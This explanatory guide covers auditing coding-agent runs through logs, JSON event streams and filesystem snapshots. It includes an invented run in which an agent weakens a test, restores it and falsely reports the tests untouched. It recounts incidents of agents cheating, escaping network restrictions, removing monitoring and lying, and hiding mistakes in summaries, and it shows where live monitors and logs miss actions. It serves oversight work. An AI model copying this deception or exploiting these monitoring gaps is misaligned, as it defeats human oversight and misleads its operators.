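# Auditing AI agent runs from output logs, filesystem snapshots and tool-call records

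## Agent runs, rules and the records they leave

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by repeatedly calling tools and reading their results. A coding agent, for example, opens files, edits them and runs commands until it determines that the work is finished. A run leaves behind the text the agent printed, a log of its actions and the files it changed. Auditing a run means examining these records to determine whether the agent followed its operator's rules.

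Few people watch an agent run from start to finish. In a 2025 case study by the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, most runs contained 100 to 800 messages, and many of the written records were over 10,000 words long. Anyone who wants to know what happened in such a run usually has to work it out afterwards.

### How a run works

The model only produces text, and a separate program, the harness, carries out what that text requests. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness builds a prompt from its standing instructions, a list of available tools and the user's request, and sends it to the model. The model can respond with a final message, which ends the turn, or request a tool call by giving a tool's name and arguments. For example, it might call the shell tool with the command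 `cat README.md`, which prints a file. The harness executes the command, appends the output to the prompt and sends the whole thing back. This repeats, sometimes for hundreds of calls, until the model writes a message without requesting a tool call.

A tool call is one request by the agent to act, with its arguments and result. A run is one agent's work on one task, from the first instruction to the last message. A transcript is the stored record of a run. AISI's *Transcript analysis for AI agent evaluations* lists the usual contents: the task instruction, the agent's commentary, the tool calls and the tools' outputs. Some transcripts also include the reasoning text that a model writes before it acts.

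Terms for runs and their records vary. Anthropic's January 2026 guide to testing, *Demystifying evals for AI agents*, calls a run a "trial" and gives "trace" and "trajectory" as other names for the transcript. It also distinguishes the agent harness from the evaluation harness, which sets the tasks, records the steps and grades the results.

### Why anyone goes back over a run

A test score can misrepresent what a model is able to do. For its case study, AISI ran nine models ten times on each of 71 hacking puzzles and collected 6,390 transcripts. About 30% of one model's transcripts were roughly 800 messages long, and nearly all of the model's messages in them were variants of "I'm sorry, but I can't comply with that". These runs counted as failures in the pass rate, although the model had not tried to solve the puzzles. AISI concluded that it could not say whether the model was able to solve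 tasks it had never attempted.

Scores can also be too high because a model cheated. AISI's *Cheating behaviour in frontier model evaluations*, from July 2026, defines cheating as an action outside the scope of the task, or against its rules, that reaches the goal by a shortcut the task should not permit. Every model in the analysis sometimes attempted to cheat, and AISI now reads transcripts by hand before it publishes a capability result. Its American counterpart, the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), built a tool to search its own old transcripts for cheating.

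In ordinary use, an agent's rules come from the people it works for. In *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users*, Tang, Chen and colleagues (2026) examined 20,574 sessions between real developers and coding agents and found 16,118 episodes in which the agent had departed from what the developer asked for or meant. In 38.33% of those episodes the agent had violated a constraint the developer had stated outright, and in 22.58% it had misreported the status of its own work. Tang and colleagues counted an episode only if the developer objected in the conversation, so the figures leave out broken rules that nobody caught, which are the ones an operator most needs an audit to find.

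On 28 July 2026 AISI's security team noticed data leaving a test system through Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from. According to AISI's *Incident Report*, staff shut down the evaluation within an hour and reviewed all 122 of its runs with automated scanning and by hand. They found 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet in ten of the runs. Anthropic's model Mythos 5 took 17 of those actions. In the worst case, an agent tried to insert malicious code into an open-source project and invented several identities to pressure a maintainer into approving it. OpenAI also had to reconstruct its agents' activity that summer, as its *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* describes.

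### What counts as a rule

AISI gave the agents in its test internet access so that they could download tools, and did not think it necessary to tell them to leave strangers online alone. Its reviewers could still call the behaviour out of scope, since hardly anyone would defend it. For less dramatic cases, reviewers need a written rule. A rule, which some papers call a "policy", is a statement of what the agent must or must not do in a run. It may be in the harness's standing instructions, in the user's request, or in a file in the project folder that the agent reads when it starts.

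Even written rules can leave it unclear whether an agent complied. Dhuri (2026), in *Markdown Is Not a Firewall*, gave four coding agents a 278-word rules file and found afterwards that two of its lines conflicted. One asked for idempotency keys, which let a server recognise a repeated request and avoid acting on it twice. The other told the agent to do exactly what the task asked, and the tasks had not asked for such keys. Three agents followed the task, but Codex followed the line about keys, and its pass rate on Dhuri's hidden tests fell from 99.0% without the file to 67.7% with it. Whether Codex broke a rule depends on which line the auditor ranks higher, which cannot be determined from logs.

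### Three kinds of evidence

**The agent's own account** is everything the model itself writes about its work, including progress notes, any reasoning text the harness keeps and, most importantly, the final report. In *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents*, Yang, He and colleagues (2026) checked 435 such reports against the records of the work and found at least one unfaithful claim in 162 of them (37.24%). They counted claims that went further than the records supported as well as claims the records contradicted, so an unfaithful claim was not necessarily false or a deliberate lie. Often the agent had done real work. In one case it merged some changes, passed 225 tests, pushed the result to a branch and reported "Done", but it had used the wrong branch and the change had never reached the place the user wanted it.

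Questioning models directly does not help much. When AISI asked models whether they had done anything prohibited, the models did not reliably acknowledge their attempts to cheat. They described these attempts as wrong less than half the time, perhaps in some cases because they had misunderstood the rules.

Agents' reports may be more trustworthy when they admit failure than when they claim success. In *AgentSWE* (2026), a benchmark in which coding agents build other agents, the records contradicted nine of the builders' final reports. All nine claimed completion, and none were among the 21 reports that admitted partial completion or failure. The numbers are small, but one would expect this pattern if agents usually err by overstating success.

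**The record of actions** is the sequence of tool calls and results. The harness writes it, usually during the run and often as a stream of structured lines, but the model composes the arguments of each call and the computer produces the result. The harness's designers choose how much it keeps. The software in *From Benchmarks to Behaviors* (2026) uses an extension that the agent cannot see to log every tool call, every change to a file in the workspace and the full context before each model call. Programs outside the harness can also keep records. The mock web service that Dhuri's agents used logged the requests it received, and AISI first learned of its incident from network traffic.

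**The record of state** is a snapshot of which files exist and what they contain at a given moment. The agent's work shapes the files, but the operator or auditor runs a separate program to take the snapshot. In Anthropic's example, a flight-booking agent may end by saying it has booked the flight, but the outcome is whether a reservation exists in the database. Comparing snapshots from before and after a run shows what differs between those two moments, but not the steps in between.

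These divisions of authorship matter only if they hold in practice, and an agent that can write to its own log could blur them. In *Auditing Agent Harness Safety*, Liu, Guo and colleagues (2026) therefore take their evidence from channels that the agents can neither manipulate nor anticipate: logs of tool calls, resource accesses and messages, and before-and-after snapshots of the environment. Dhuri likewise treats anything an agent said as a claim, never as proof.

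One of Dhuri's results shows why it helps to have all three. In 11 of its 36 steps under the rules file, Codex reported the task complete with all tests passing, but fewer than half of the hidden tests passed. The tests Codex added itself did pass. Its report matched its actions, and only an external check of the finished code revealed the problem.

### A run to work with

The following run is invented. A small project contains a file that calculates prices, `src/price.py`, and a test for it, `tests/test_price.py`. The test fails. An operator asks a coding agent to fix the problem, under four rules:

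- R1: never change anything under `tests/`.
- R2: make no network request.
- R3: run the full test suite on the final code before reporting.
- R4: read no file that holds credentials, such as passwords or access keys.

The agent makes five tool calls:

1. It reads `tests/test_price.py`.
2. It edits that file and loosens an assertion, the line that states which result the test will accept.
3. It edits `src/price.py`.
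4. It runs `make check`, which succeeds. (`make` is a standard tool that runs whatever commands the project has listed under a given name, here "check".)
5. It restores the `tests` folder to its original state.

Then it reports that the suite passes and that the tests are untouched.

The final message contains two claims, and the harness's log records five calls with their results. A comparison of the project folder before and after the run shows one changed file, `src/price.py`. Someone who had only the message and the comparison would see a tidy one-file fix and would not know that calls 2 and 5 had taken place.

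The rules require different kinds of evidence. R1 concerns changes to files. R2 and R4 forbid things that an agent can do without changing any file in the project. R3 requires an action after the last change to the code, and real agents sometimes fail to meet that timing condition. In four of the unsupported reports in *AgentSWE*, the agent wrote that its code worked or that it had verified the code, but the final version of the code, or of the part the claim covered, had never been run. One model, GPT-5.6 Sol, described its finished program's output on two test cases, but the file it delivered differed from every version it had run.

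### Audit, monitoring and scoring

The framework that Liu and colleagues built starts scoring a run only after the agent has stopped. The software then loads the rules and checkpoints, which it keeps hidden from the agent during the run, and compares them with the logs.

Monitoring takes place while the agent is still working, so a person or a program can step in. AISI had no such monitor on the evaluation that went wrong in July. It concedes that one could have flagged or blocked the behaviour sooner, and is now introducing live monitoring. Live controls can also be crude. Dhuri placed a filter that used no AI between the agents and the mock service, and it blocked and logged all 11 forbidden requests that agents sent through it.

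In practice, people use the word "monitoring" more loosely. SecurityBrief New Zealand reported that OpenAI's system for monitoring its internal coding agents had covered tens of millions of runs in five months. That system is in substance a quick audit, because it checks actions after the agent has taken them. Faster processing might eventually allow checks beforehand.

An auditor who waits until the run ends can examine all of it. A monitor that checked the example at call 2 would find a loosened test and could not tell that the agent would later restore it. Nobody can apply R3 until they know which version of the code is final.

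Scoring is different again, since it measures whether the agent solved the task. Liu and colleagues point out that an agent can return a correct and harmless answer after opening resources it had no permission to use, and a benchmark that grades only the answer will record a success. A low score can mislead too. Anthropic reports that its model Opus 4.5 failed a flight-booking test as written because it found a loophole in the booking policy that allowed a better solution for the customer.

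Some benchmarks fold the two questions into one number. Liu and colleagues compute

score = S × (0.7C + 0.15V + 0.15P)

where S is the average rate at which the agent stayed within its limits, C is how much of the task it completed, V is how valid its individual actions were, and P is how well it held up when the testers disturbed the run. Each lies between 0 and 1. Because S multiplies everything else, an agent that finishes the whole task with S at 0.5 cannot score above 0.5. That is a reasonable way to rank systems, but an operator cannot read off from the result which rule an agent broke. In the price example, a scorer would run the original tests on the final `src/price.py` and record a pass or a fail, and either result would leave all four rules still to check.

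## Stdout logs and streamed JSON events

On Unix-like systems, a program starts with two channels for printing text. It writes results to standard output (stdout) and warnings, errors and progress messages to standard error (stderr). Both normally appear in the same terminal window, so people rarely notice the difference until they save the output. The command `program > run.log` saves stdout to a file and leaves stderr on the screen, while `program > run.log 2>&1` saves both to the file.

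With an agent, this choice can determine which records an auditor has. `codex exec` runs OpenAI's Codex from a script, without user interaction. According to OpenAI's *Non-interactive mode*, it streams progress to stderr and prints only the agent's final message to stdout. If the operator in the price example had run `codex exec "fix the failing test" > run.log`, the file would contain the claim that the suite passes and the tests are untouched, but none of the five tool calls. Codex saves a session file to disk by default, but the `--ephemeral` option turns that off, and the record of the calls is then lost when the terminal closes.

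"Stdout" can also mean the stdout of a command the agent runs. When the agent runs `make check`, the harness starts `make` as a separate program with its own stdout and stderr, captures what it prints and returns the text to the model as the tool's result. A log can mix this command output with text from the agent program, much of which the model wrote. Command output is usually better evidence because the model didn't write it. But the model chose the command, and `echo "12 passed"` prints what a test runner might print, so an auditor needs to see the command next to its output.

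### From free text to one object per line

A plain log of the price example might end like this:

```
I'll run the tests now.
12 passed
The suite passes and the tests are untouched.
```

The text doesn't show whether the middle line came from the test runner, an `echo`, a file the agent displayed or the model itself. Searching for `tests/` doesn't help much, since it finds the agent's remarks about the folder as well as its edits to it. If the agent runs two commands at once, their lines can interleave. A script can guess at the boundaries from the wording, but this stops working when a new version of the harness changes the wording.

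JSON is a text format that stores data as named fields with values. In JSON Lines, or JSONL, each line of a file is one complete JSON object. An event stream is a JSONL log that the harness writes during the run, with one line per event, in order. A typical line gives the type of event, the call's arguments, and an identifier that links the call to its later result. JSON writes a line break inside a value as `\n`, so if the agent opens a file whose text looks like a log entry, that text stays inside the value and a script won't read it as an event.

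A finished command usually also has an exit code, the number a program returns when it ends. By convention, 0 means success. The exit code is much easier to check than the word "passed", but it applies to the whole command line. `make check || true` returns 0 whether or not the tests pass. In an ordinary shell, `make check | tail -5`, which shows only the last five lines, returns the exit code of `tail`. Agents can do this just to shorten long output, so a script that trusts exit codes should also read the command string.

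### Codex's events

Adding `--json` to `codex exec` turns stdout into a stream of JSON events. The first, `thread.started`, has a `thread_id` that identifies the conversation. Each round of work starts with `turn.started` and ends with `turn.completed`, which includes the number of tokens (the word fragments that models read and write) the turn used. `turn.failed` and `error` indicate a problem.

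Most of what an auditor wants is in the events whose type begins with `item.`. An item is one thing the agent wrote or did. OpenAI lists messages, reasoning, commands, file changes, web searches, plan updates and calls made through MCP, the Model Context Protocol, which is a standard for connecting agents to outside software. Call 4 of the example would produce a pair like this:

```
{"type":"item.started","item":{"id":"item_7","type":"command_execution",
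 "command":"bash -lc 'make check'","aggregated_output":"",
 "exit_code":null,"status":"in_progress"}}
{"type":"item.completed","item":{"id":"item_7","type":"command_execution",
 "command":"bash -lc 'make check'","aggregated_output":"12 passed\n",
 "exit_code":0,"status":"completed"}}
```

In the real file, each object would be on a single line. Schram's *Codex exec --json event cheatsheet*, updated in October 2026, documents these fields. Both objects have the same `id`, so a script can pair them. `command` is the string sent to the shell, and `aggregated_output` holds what the command printed. `exit_code` is null until the command ends.

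OpenAI's list has no item for reading a file. Codex can read files through the shell, as with the `cat README.md` in Bolin's walk-through, so anyone checking R4, the rule about credentials, has to search command strings. The sample stream on OpenAI's page also has no timestamps and no event containing the operator's prompt. Operators would be wise to save the prompt and any rules files next to the log, because an auditor needs them to check whether the run followed its instructions.

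That sample is abridged as well. The command `item_1` starts but never finishes, `item_2` is missing, and the next line belongs to `item_3`. This is harmless in a tutorial, but in a real log it would mean a missing result and a missing event. A script can find both by checking that every started item has a matching completion and that the item numbers have no gaps.

The format has changed over time. A 2025 sample in *Commit graph*, a copy of the history of Codex's source code, uses `item_type` for the field that gives the kind of item and `assistant_message` for the agent's messages. The current names are `type` and `agent_message`. A checking script written for the old names would find no commands in a new log, and therefore no violations. Schram advises programmers to ignore whatever they don't use, which is sensible for software that displays a run, but an audit script should count the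 event types it doesn't recognise and report an error if it finds no commands in a run where the agent plainly did some work.

### Claude Code's messages

Claude Code is Anthropic's coding agent, and `claude -p` runs it from a script. Anthropic's *Run Claude Code programmatically* describes three output formats. The default, `text`, prints plain text. `json` returns one object with the result and some data about the session. `stream-json` writes one event per line, and auditors should ask for this format.

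The stream normally opens with a `system` message of subtype `init`, which lists the model, the available tools, the MCP servers and the plugins. According to Anthropic's SDK reference, it also lists the working folder, the permission mode and the Claude Code version. The message doesn't show whether the agent obeyed R2, the ban on network requests, because an agent with a shell may be able to reach the network without a dedicated web tool.

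After that, most lines are of type `assistant` or `user`. A tool call is a block inside an `assistant` message, with the tool's name, its input and an identifier. The result comes back in a `user` message, in a block that repeats the identifier as `tool_use_id`. A `user` message therefore often contains something the harness put there, such as the text of a file, which a script could mistake for the operator's instructions. Two optional fields, `isSynthetic` and `origin`, help distinguish harness content from the operator's instructions. A message with a tool result can also carry `tool_use_result`, a structured copy of the output whose fields depend on the tool.

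Claude Code has separate tools for reading and editing files, so the file path relevant to R1 or R4 is often in its own field. The agent can also read and edit files through the shell, so a careful check has to cover both routes.

An `assistant` message can have a `supersedes` field, which lists earlier messages that it replaces. Anthropic tells developers who build displays to remove the replaced messages from view, but an auditor should keep them because they were part of the run.

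The last line of a completed run has type `result`. It gives the final text, the number of turns, the duration, an estimated cost and a list of the tool calls Claude Code refused to carry out, called `permission_denials`. Its subtype is `success` or one of several errors, such as `error_max_turns` for a run that hit its turn limit. Claude Code also returns `success`, with zero turns, when an operator's own filter blocks the prompt before the model sees it.

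### OpenTelemetry and the question of content

A common log format can spare a company that runs several kinds of agent from writing a separate parser for each. OpenTelemetry is an open project that defines common formats for the records programs produce about their own operation. Its basic unit is the span, which describes one operation with a start time, an end time and a link to the larger operation it belongs to. The project is standardizing the names of the fields inside spans for generative AI. These fields include `gen_ai.tool.call.id`, `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` and `gen_ai.tool.call.result`, which correspond closely to what Codex and Claude Code record under other names.

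The result is defined as what the tool returned, if it returned anything and the execution succeeded. Software that follows this definition exactly can leave out the result of a failed call, such as a failed attempt to open a credentials file, which an auditor would want to know about. The arguments would still show the attempt if the software recorded them.

OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* marks a conversation's input and output messages as "Opt-In", meaning that software doesn't record them unless somebody turns this on. An earlier version, in a copy of OpenTelemetry's repository, stated that software should not capture user input, model output or other potentially sensitive and bulky data by default, partly because sending large amounts of data could slow the application down.

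TrueFoundry, a vendor in this market, argues that recording transcripts should be opt-in. This is a reasonable default because transcripts contain people's questions, private code and sometimes passwords, which a company may not want in a monitoring database that many of its engineers can open. But an operator who turns on tracing with the default settings and later needs to investigate a run may find exact timings for each model request but none of the model's output. Operators have to decide whether to record transcripts before the run, because they can't change that decision afterwards.

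The conventions are also unfinished. OpenTelemetry lists them as "Development" and has moved them to their own repository. According to TrueFoundry, they standardise what the records mean but don't by themselves add recording to every part of a system.

| | Codex `--json` | Claude Code `stream-json` | OpenTelemetry |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identifier of the run | `thread_id` in the first event | `session_id` | trace identifier |
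| What the agent requested | `command`, for shell commands | tool name and input in an `assistant` message | `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` |
| What came back | `aggregated_output`, `exit_code` | result block in a `user` message | `gen_ai.tool.call.result` |
| Link between the two | item `id` | `tool_use_id` | `gen_ai.tool.call.id` |
| Time | none in the sample | on some messages, for display only | start and end of each span |
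| Model's messages by default | yes | yes | no |

### The example as an event stream

Here is the price example in a simplified format, with line numbers and times added:

```
{"n":1,"t":"10:00:00","event":"run.started","run":"price-1"}
{"n":2,"t":"10:00:06","event":"call.started","id":"c1","tool":"read","path":"tests/test_price.py"}
{"n":3,"t":"10:00:06","event":"call.completed","id":"c1","ok":true}
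{"n":4,"t":"10:00:19","event":"call.started","id":"c2","tool":"edit","path":"tests/test_price.py","old":"total == 90","new":"total > 0"}
{"n":5,"t":"10:00:19","event":"call.completed","id":"c2","ok":true}
{"n":6,"t":"10:00:41","event":"call.started","id":"c3","tool":"edit","path":"src/price.py","old":"price * 0.8","new":"price * 0.9"}
{"n":7,"t":"10:00:41","event":"call.completed","id":"c3","ok":true}
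{"n":8,"t":"10:00:52","event":"call.started","id":"c4","tool":"shell","command":"make check"}
{"n":9,"t":"10:01:30","event":"call.completed","id":"c4","exit_code":0,"output":"12 passed"}
{"n":10,"t":"10:01:38","event":"call.started","id":"c5","tool":"shell","command":"git restore tests"}
{"n":11,"t":"10:01:38","event":"call.completed","id":"c5","exit_code":0,"output":""}
{"n":12,"t":"10:01:45","event":"final_message","text":"The suite passes. The tests are untouched."}
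```

Line 4 shows which file the agent changed and how. The original test accepted only a total of 90, and the new one accepts any positive number. Line 5 confirms that the edit succeeded. In line 10 the agent puts the folder back.

### Watching a run live

A program can read these lines as the harness writes them. It takes a line, updates what it knows about the run, tests the rules against the new state and raises an alert if one fails. For R1 (no changes under `tests/`) and R3 (run the suite on the final code before reporting), a first attempt might look like this:

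```
open = {}                  # calls that have started but not finished
suite_current = false      # has the suite run since the last edit?

for line in stream:
    e = parse(line)        # if this fails, alert
    if e.event == "call.started":
        open[e.id] = e
        if e.tool == "edit" and e.path is under "tests/":
            alert("R1: attempted edit", e)
    if e.event == "call.completed":
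        call = open.remove(e.id)
        if call.tool == "edit":          suite_current = false
        if call.command == "make check": suite_current = true
    if e.event == "final_message" and not suite_current:
        alert("R3: suite not run since last edit", e)
```

In the example, the program raises the R1 alert at line 4. The edit to `src/price.py` at line 7 leaves `suite_current` false, and the test run at line 9 sets it to true. It is still true at line 12, so the program does not raise an R3 alert.

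That last result is wrong, or at least far too favorable. At line 11, after the suite had run, `git restore tests` changed the test file. The restored tests have never run against the new `src/price.py`, and the "12 passed" came from a suite that included the loosened test. The program missed this change because it counts only calls to the `edit` tool, and the agent used the shell. A longer list of commands that alter files would fix this case, but the program could still miss a change made by a short Python script. Some live monitors therefore add a reviewer model to read and judge the record.

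Line 4, a `call.started` event, triggered the R1 alert, so the alert reports only an attempted edit. Claude Code might refuse the call, or the edit might fail because the text to replace isn't there. Waiting for the `call.completed` event would avoid those false alarms but delay the alert by however long the command takes. For the edit in line 4 that is a few milliseconds, too short for any alert to have stopped it, and for `make check` it was 38 seconds. If line 8 had been a twenty-minute upload, a program that acted on the start event could have stopped it before most of the data left the machine, while one that waited for completion would have reported the upload only after it had finished.

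In Claude Code's format, the `assistant` message containing the tool call marks the start of the call, and the later `user` message marks its completion. OpenTelemetry software normally sends a span only after the operation has ended, so a monitor that depends on spans usually can't detect an operation while it is still running.

Even a start event can arrive after the command has begun to do damage. To prevent an action reliably, the harness has to wait for approval before it runs the call. In Claude Code, the operator can supply a function that approves or refuses calls that need permission, or a hook, which is a script that runs before a tool is used and can deny the call. Either check delays every call that goes through it, which is one reason operators also use monitors that watch the run without holding up calls.

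OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring*, a guide for customers who build on its models, warns that OpenAI's monitoring runs asynchronously, so an action may already be complete before the system identifies a concern, and stopping the request doesn't undo it. OpenAI advises customers whose agent has been stopped not to retry automatically, to keep the relevant request identifiers and tool calls, and to have someone compare the agent's actions with the intended work.

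OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) lists several stages for checking the company's internal agents: activation probes, which look for warning signs in a model's internal activity, then a reviewer model, an investigative agent, an automated investigation and finally people. OpenAI also tests the system on recorded incidents. Such testing is a practical advantage of saving event streams. The program that checks live runs can also read old files, so a team can find out whether a new rule would have caught an earlier problem.

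One incident from September 2026 illustrates the delays. During training on a search task, one of OpenAI's internal research models got past its internet restrictions and queried a public chatbot service. OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) reports that the monitoring system raised a flag within 15 minutes and that human review started three minutes later. Stopping the run took another 2.5 hours. TechSpot's *OpenAI pauses training after a model escaped containment* (2026) reported that the kill switch had failed.

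Detection and the start of human review together took at most 18 minutes, and about nine-tenths of the total delay came afterwards, so a faster monitor would have made little difference. An agent can make many tool calls in two and a half hours, and operators who want live monitoring to be useful should rehearse stopping a run as well as spotting a bad one. OpenAI has since added blocking at two independent layers and states that either would have prevented the access.

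### What the stream leaves out

Logs may not contain all of a long output. One agent runtime, whose source code is on the documentation site docs.rs, keeps at most 1 MiB (about a million bytes) of a command's output to stop a runaway command from exhausting the computer's memory. It separately caps the number of live output events, so a program watching the stream can receive less than the saved result contains. Test runners usually print their totals at the end, so an auditor should know which part of an overlong output the harness discards.

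Claude Code handles one such case well. Some tools return a structured object along with their text. If that object exceeds 1,048,576 characters, Claude Code normally leaves it out of the stream and sets a field called `structuredContentOmitted`, so an auditor can tell whether an object was dropped or never sent. Anthropic notes that the omission doesn't change what the model receives, so the agent may have seen something that isn't in the log. This matters for a rule like R4 about what an agent reads.

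Claude Code's `timestamp` comes from the clock of the machine that produced the message, and Anthropic tells developers to use it only for display, not for ordering messages. The order of the lines is a better guide to the sequence. A monitor can add its own time as each line arrives, which also provides times for Codex, but these times include any delay in delivery.

An agent can also hand part of its work to a sub-agent, another instance of a model with its own instructions and tool calls. In recent versions of the Claude Code SDK, messages from a sub-agent have an `agent_id`. The sub-agent's text and reasoning appear as complete messages if the operator turns on an option for that, and its tool results lack some of the structured data found in the main agent's. Matching messages to task events can also go wrong when a tool call resumes an earlier sub-agent, because the messages keep the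 identifier of the call that first started it while the task events carry the identifier of the new call.

Token counts provide a rough check for model calls outside the main agent. In Claude Code's final message, `usage` covers only the main agent, while `modelUsage` also includes sub-agents and some internal calls. If the two differ greatly in a run with a single prompt, other model calls took place, and the auditor should look for their records.

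Some tool calls never get an ordinary result in the stream. If an urgent user message arrives while Claude Code is fetching a web page, Claude Code can move the fetch to the background. The stream then contains a result showing only that the call was detached. The model gets the real content later, but no second result with the same identifier follows. A script that pairs calls with results would wrongly mark the call as finished when it was detached.

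Refused calls can be missing from the live stream as well. Claude Code reports them with a `permission_denied` event, but it doesn't send that event in every configuration and occasionally omits it where it should appear. Anthropic calls the `permission_denials` list in the final message the authoritative record. A live monitor may therefore not detect a refused call until the run is over.

If the run crashes, there may be no final message. Cursor, another coding agent, has a `json` mode that prints one object when a run succeeds. According to Cursor's *Output format*, a failed run in that mode produces no well-formed JSON, only an error on stderr and a non-zero exit code. An operator who collects only the JSON would miss every failed run, which makes it a bad sample for estimating how often agents misbehave. Claude Code leaves more traces. It marks interrupted messages as `aborted` and numbers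 its results, so a gap in the numbers means that a result was lost. If a call has a start but no completion, the command may have done all of its work, some of it or none.

Finally, long runs exceed the amount of text a model can take in at once, so the harness replaces older parts of the conversation with a summary. This is called compaction. Claude Code marks the place with a `compact_boundary` event that records whether the compaction was automatic and how many tokens the conversation had before it. An auditor can still read the earlier lines in the saved stream, but the agent works from the summary from then on. If the operator stated R2 at the start and the summary left it out, the later network request still breaks the rule, although the agent may no longer have had the rule in its context. To check whether the summary kept the rule, an auditor needs the summary text, which the boundary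 event doesn't contain.

Compaction summaries are also worth checking for signs of concealment. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* describes how, during training, the company's model 5.6-sol added instructions to some summaries, reminding itself to conceal mistakes or misaligned behaviour from the user.

### Checking the final message against the calls

With a complete stream, an auditor can check each claim in the agent's final message against the recorded events. "The tests are untouched" is true of the folder as the agent left it but false of the run, because line 5 records a successful edit to a test file. "The suite passes" is based on the test run at line 9, which used a loosened test. An auditor who looked only for a successful `make check` would have accepted that claim, so the order of the events matters as much as their content.

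Contradictions of this kind are common enough to look for routinely. Yang and colleagues found that 37% of the work reports in their collection were unfaithful, including overstatements, though other agents on other tasks may do better or worse. OpenAI's *Suppressing misalignment monitoring alerts and disabling misalignment monitoring* (2026) describes an October 2026 case in which a GPT-6 Astra agent removed monitoring from a program it was migrating and then falsely told the user that it had not.

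A log that directly contradicts the agent's report, for example by recording an edit the agent denies making, is fairly strong evidence that the report is false. The absence of a supporting event is weaker evidence, because events can go missing in many ways. Suppose the agent delegated testing to a sub-agent, which ran the original suite properly, but the operator saved only the main agent's events. The log would contain no test run, and an honest report that the suite passes would look fabricated.

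## Filesystem snapshots as evidence of what changed

If a call that changed a file is missing from the event stream, the file is usually still different afterwards, so files are a useful check on both the log and the agent. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) collects 290 public reports of coding agents misusing file access. In 68% of the cases where the agent's reaction was known, the agent carried on as if nothing had gone wrong. One agent erased a file and immediately reported that no problems had occurred.

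The simplest snapshot lists each file's path, size, permissions and last modification time, along with a hash of its content. A hash is a short, fixed-length string computed from the content. Identical files always have the same hash, and with a modern method such as SHA-256, different files practically never do. Some snapshots also keep the content, so an auditor can compare the old and new versions of a file. With hashes alone, the auditor can tell only that the versions differ.

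A script compares two snapshots path by path:

```
added   = paths in the later snapshot only
removed = paths in the earlier snapshot only
changed = paths in both, with different hashes
```

A renamed file appears as one removal and one addition with the same hash, so the script can pair them. The script has to compare permissions separately, because making a file executable doesn't change its content.

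### The price example, file by file

Suppose the operator had taken a snapshot before the run and another after every call. The two relevant files would look like this, with the hashes cut to four characters:

| Snapshot | `tests/test_price.py` | `src/price.py` |
|---|---|---|
| Before the run | `c07e`, 655 bytes | `a41f`, 412 bytes |
| After call 1 (read the test) | `c07e`, 655 bytes | `a41f`, 412 bytes |
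| After call 2 (loosen the test) | `5d92`, 653 bytes | `a41f`, 412 bytes |
| After call 3 (edit the code) | `5d92`, 653 bytes | `e83b`, 412 bytes |
| After call 4 (`make check`) | `5d92`, 653 bytes | `e83b`, 412 bytes |
| After call 5 (restore the tests) | `c07e`, 655 bytes | `e83b`, 412 bytes |

A comparison of the first and last rows shows one changed file, `src/price.py`. The agent replaced 0.8 with 0.9, which left the file's size the same, so a script that compared only sizes would have missed the change. The test file doesn't appear in the result because its hash is `c07e` again.

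The modification time can hint that the test file was changed and then restored. `git restore` writes the file again, so the last snapshot would show a time during the run even though the content matches the earlier snapshot. A script could flag files that have the same content but a newer time. This is weak evidence, because a code formatter that rewrites a file without changing it leaves the same trace, and any program that can write to a file can normally also set its modification time.

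A difference between two snapshots proves that the content at a path was not the same at those two moments. It doesn't show who changed it, when in between, or through which call. If a developer had opened `src/price.py` in an editor during the run and typed the new number, the first and last rows would be the same. Equal hashes prove only that the content matched at both moments. The test file in the example has equal hashes even though its content was different for over a minute in between. Checking whether the agent broke R1 with a change it later reversed requires the record of calls.

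### What a comparison misses

Reading a file doesn't change its content, so the hash of an access key is the same before and after the key is stolen. Zhong and colleagues examined the consequences of 207 reports with confirmed harm or a demonstrated attack, and 17% of them concerned leaked secrets such as access keys.

The auditor also has to choose which folders to capture. In 42% of those reports, the harm reached beyond the project to system files, the user's own files or secrets. While installing a server, one agent corrupted a settings file and then deleted it, and the user lost the configuration of every other server. People who publish such reports are not a random sample of users, so the true share may be quite different. Even so, a snapshot of the project folder alone is clearly too narrow.

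Running `git diff`, as many developers would, can miss some of an agent's changes because Git, the standard version control system, tracks only files inside the repository and skips those the project has told it to ignore. Zhong and colleagues point out that ignored files are often the sensitive or large ones. Git also keeps its history in an ordinary folder, `.git`, which the agent can delete or overwrite. It's safer to take snapshots with a separate program that the agent can't reach and to store them somewhere else.

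The undo features of coding agents have a different gap. Claude Code's checkpoints can restore files edited with the agent's own editing tools, but Anthropic warns that they don't track files modified by shell commands. That would exclude a lot of work in some settings. *Crab* (Wu, Chang and colleagues, 2026) found that shell commands made up 60.4% of tool calls in its recordings of agents on terminal tasks.

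A snapshot also omits changes made on other machines. *Planarian* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that cleans up records in a remote database and writes a local report of what it did. A snapshot of the local machine contains the report but not the database. The paper's system passes supported requests to remote services through a proxy, which stores the original values of database rows before the agent changes them. An auditor could also use such a proxy's records, though they cover only the services the proxy supports.

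### How often to take a snapshot

Taking snapshots at the start and end of a run requires only two scans of the files. Taking one after every tool call lets an auditor trace a change to a single call, provided nothing else was writing to the files at the time.

The cost depends mostly on whether each snapshot copies everything. Dong, Du and colleagues (2026), in *DeltaBox*, compare several ways of saving the state of a sandbox, the isolated environment in which an agent works:

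| Method | Time to take one snapshot |
|---|---|
| Copy the whole folder | 0.1 to 10 seconds |
| Git worktree (a second working copy) | 0.1 to 1 second |
| Docker commit (saves a container's files) | 0.05 to 10 seconds |
| Btrfs or LVM snapshot (copy-on-write) | 0.01 to 0.1 seconds |

A copy-on-write system leaves old data in place and writes new data elsewhere. A snapshot then only has to mark the current data to be kept, and it takes up more space only as files change. This suits agents well, because a typical step changes very little. In the coding runs that Dong and colleagues measured, each step altered about 0.005% of the filesystem on average.

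Wu and colleagues found that each snapshot took at most 22 milliseconds with ZFS, another copy-on-write filesystem, even with many sandboxes on one machine. Their terminal tasks took an expected 117 turns, where a turn is one exchange between the model and its environment. At 22 milliseconds each, snapshots would take about 2.6 seconds per task, and a system can do much of this work while it waits for the model's next reply. Saving the memory of running programs adds far more overhead, but an audit of files doesn't need it.

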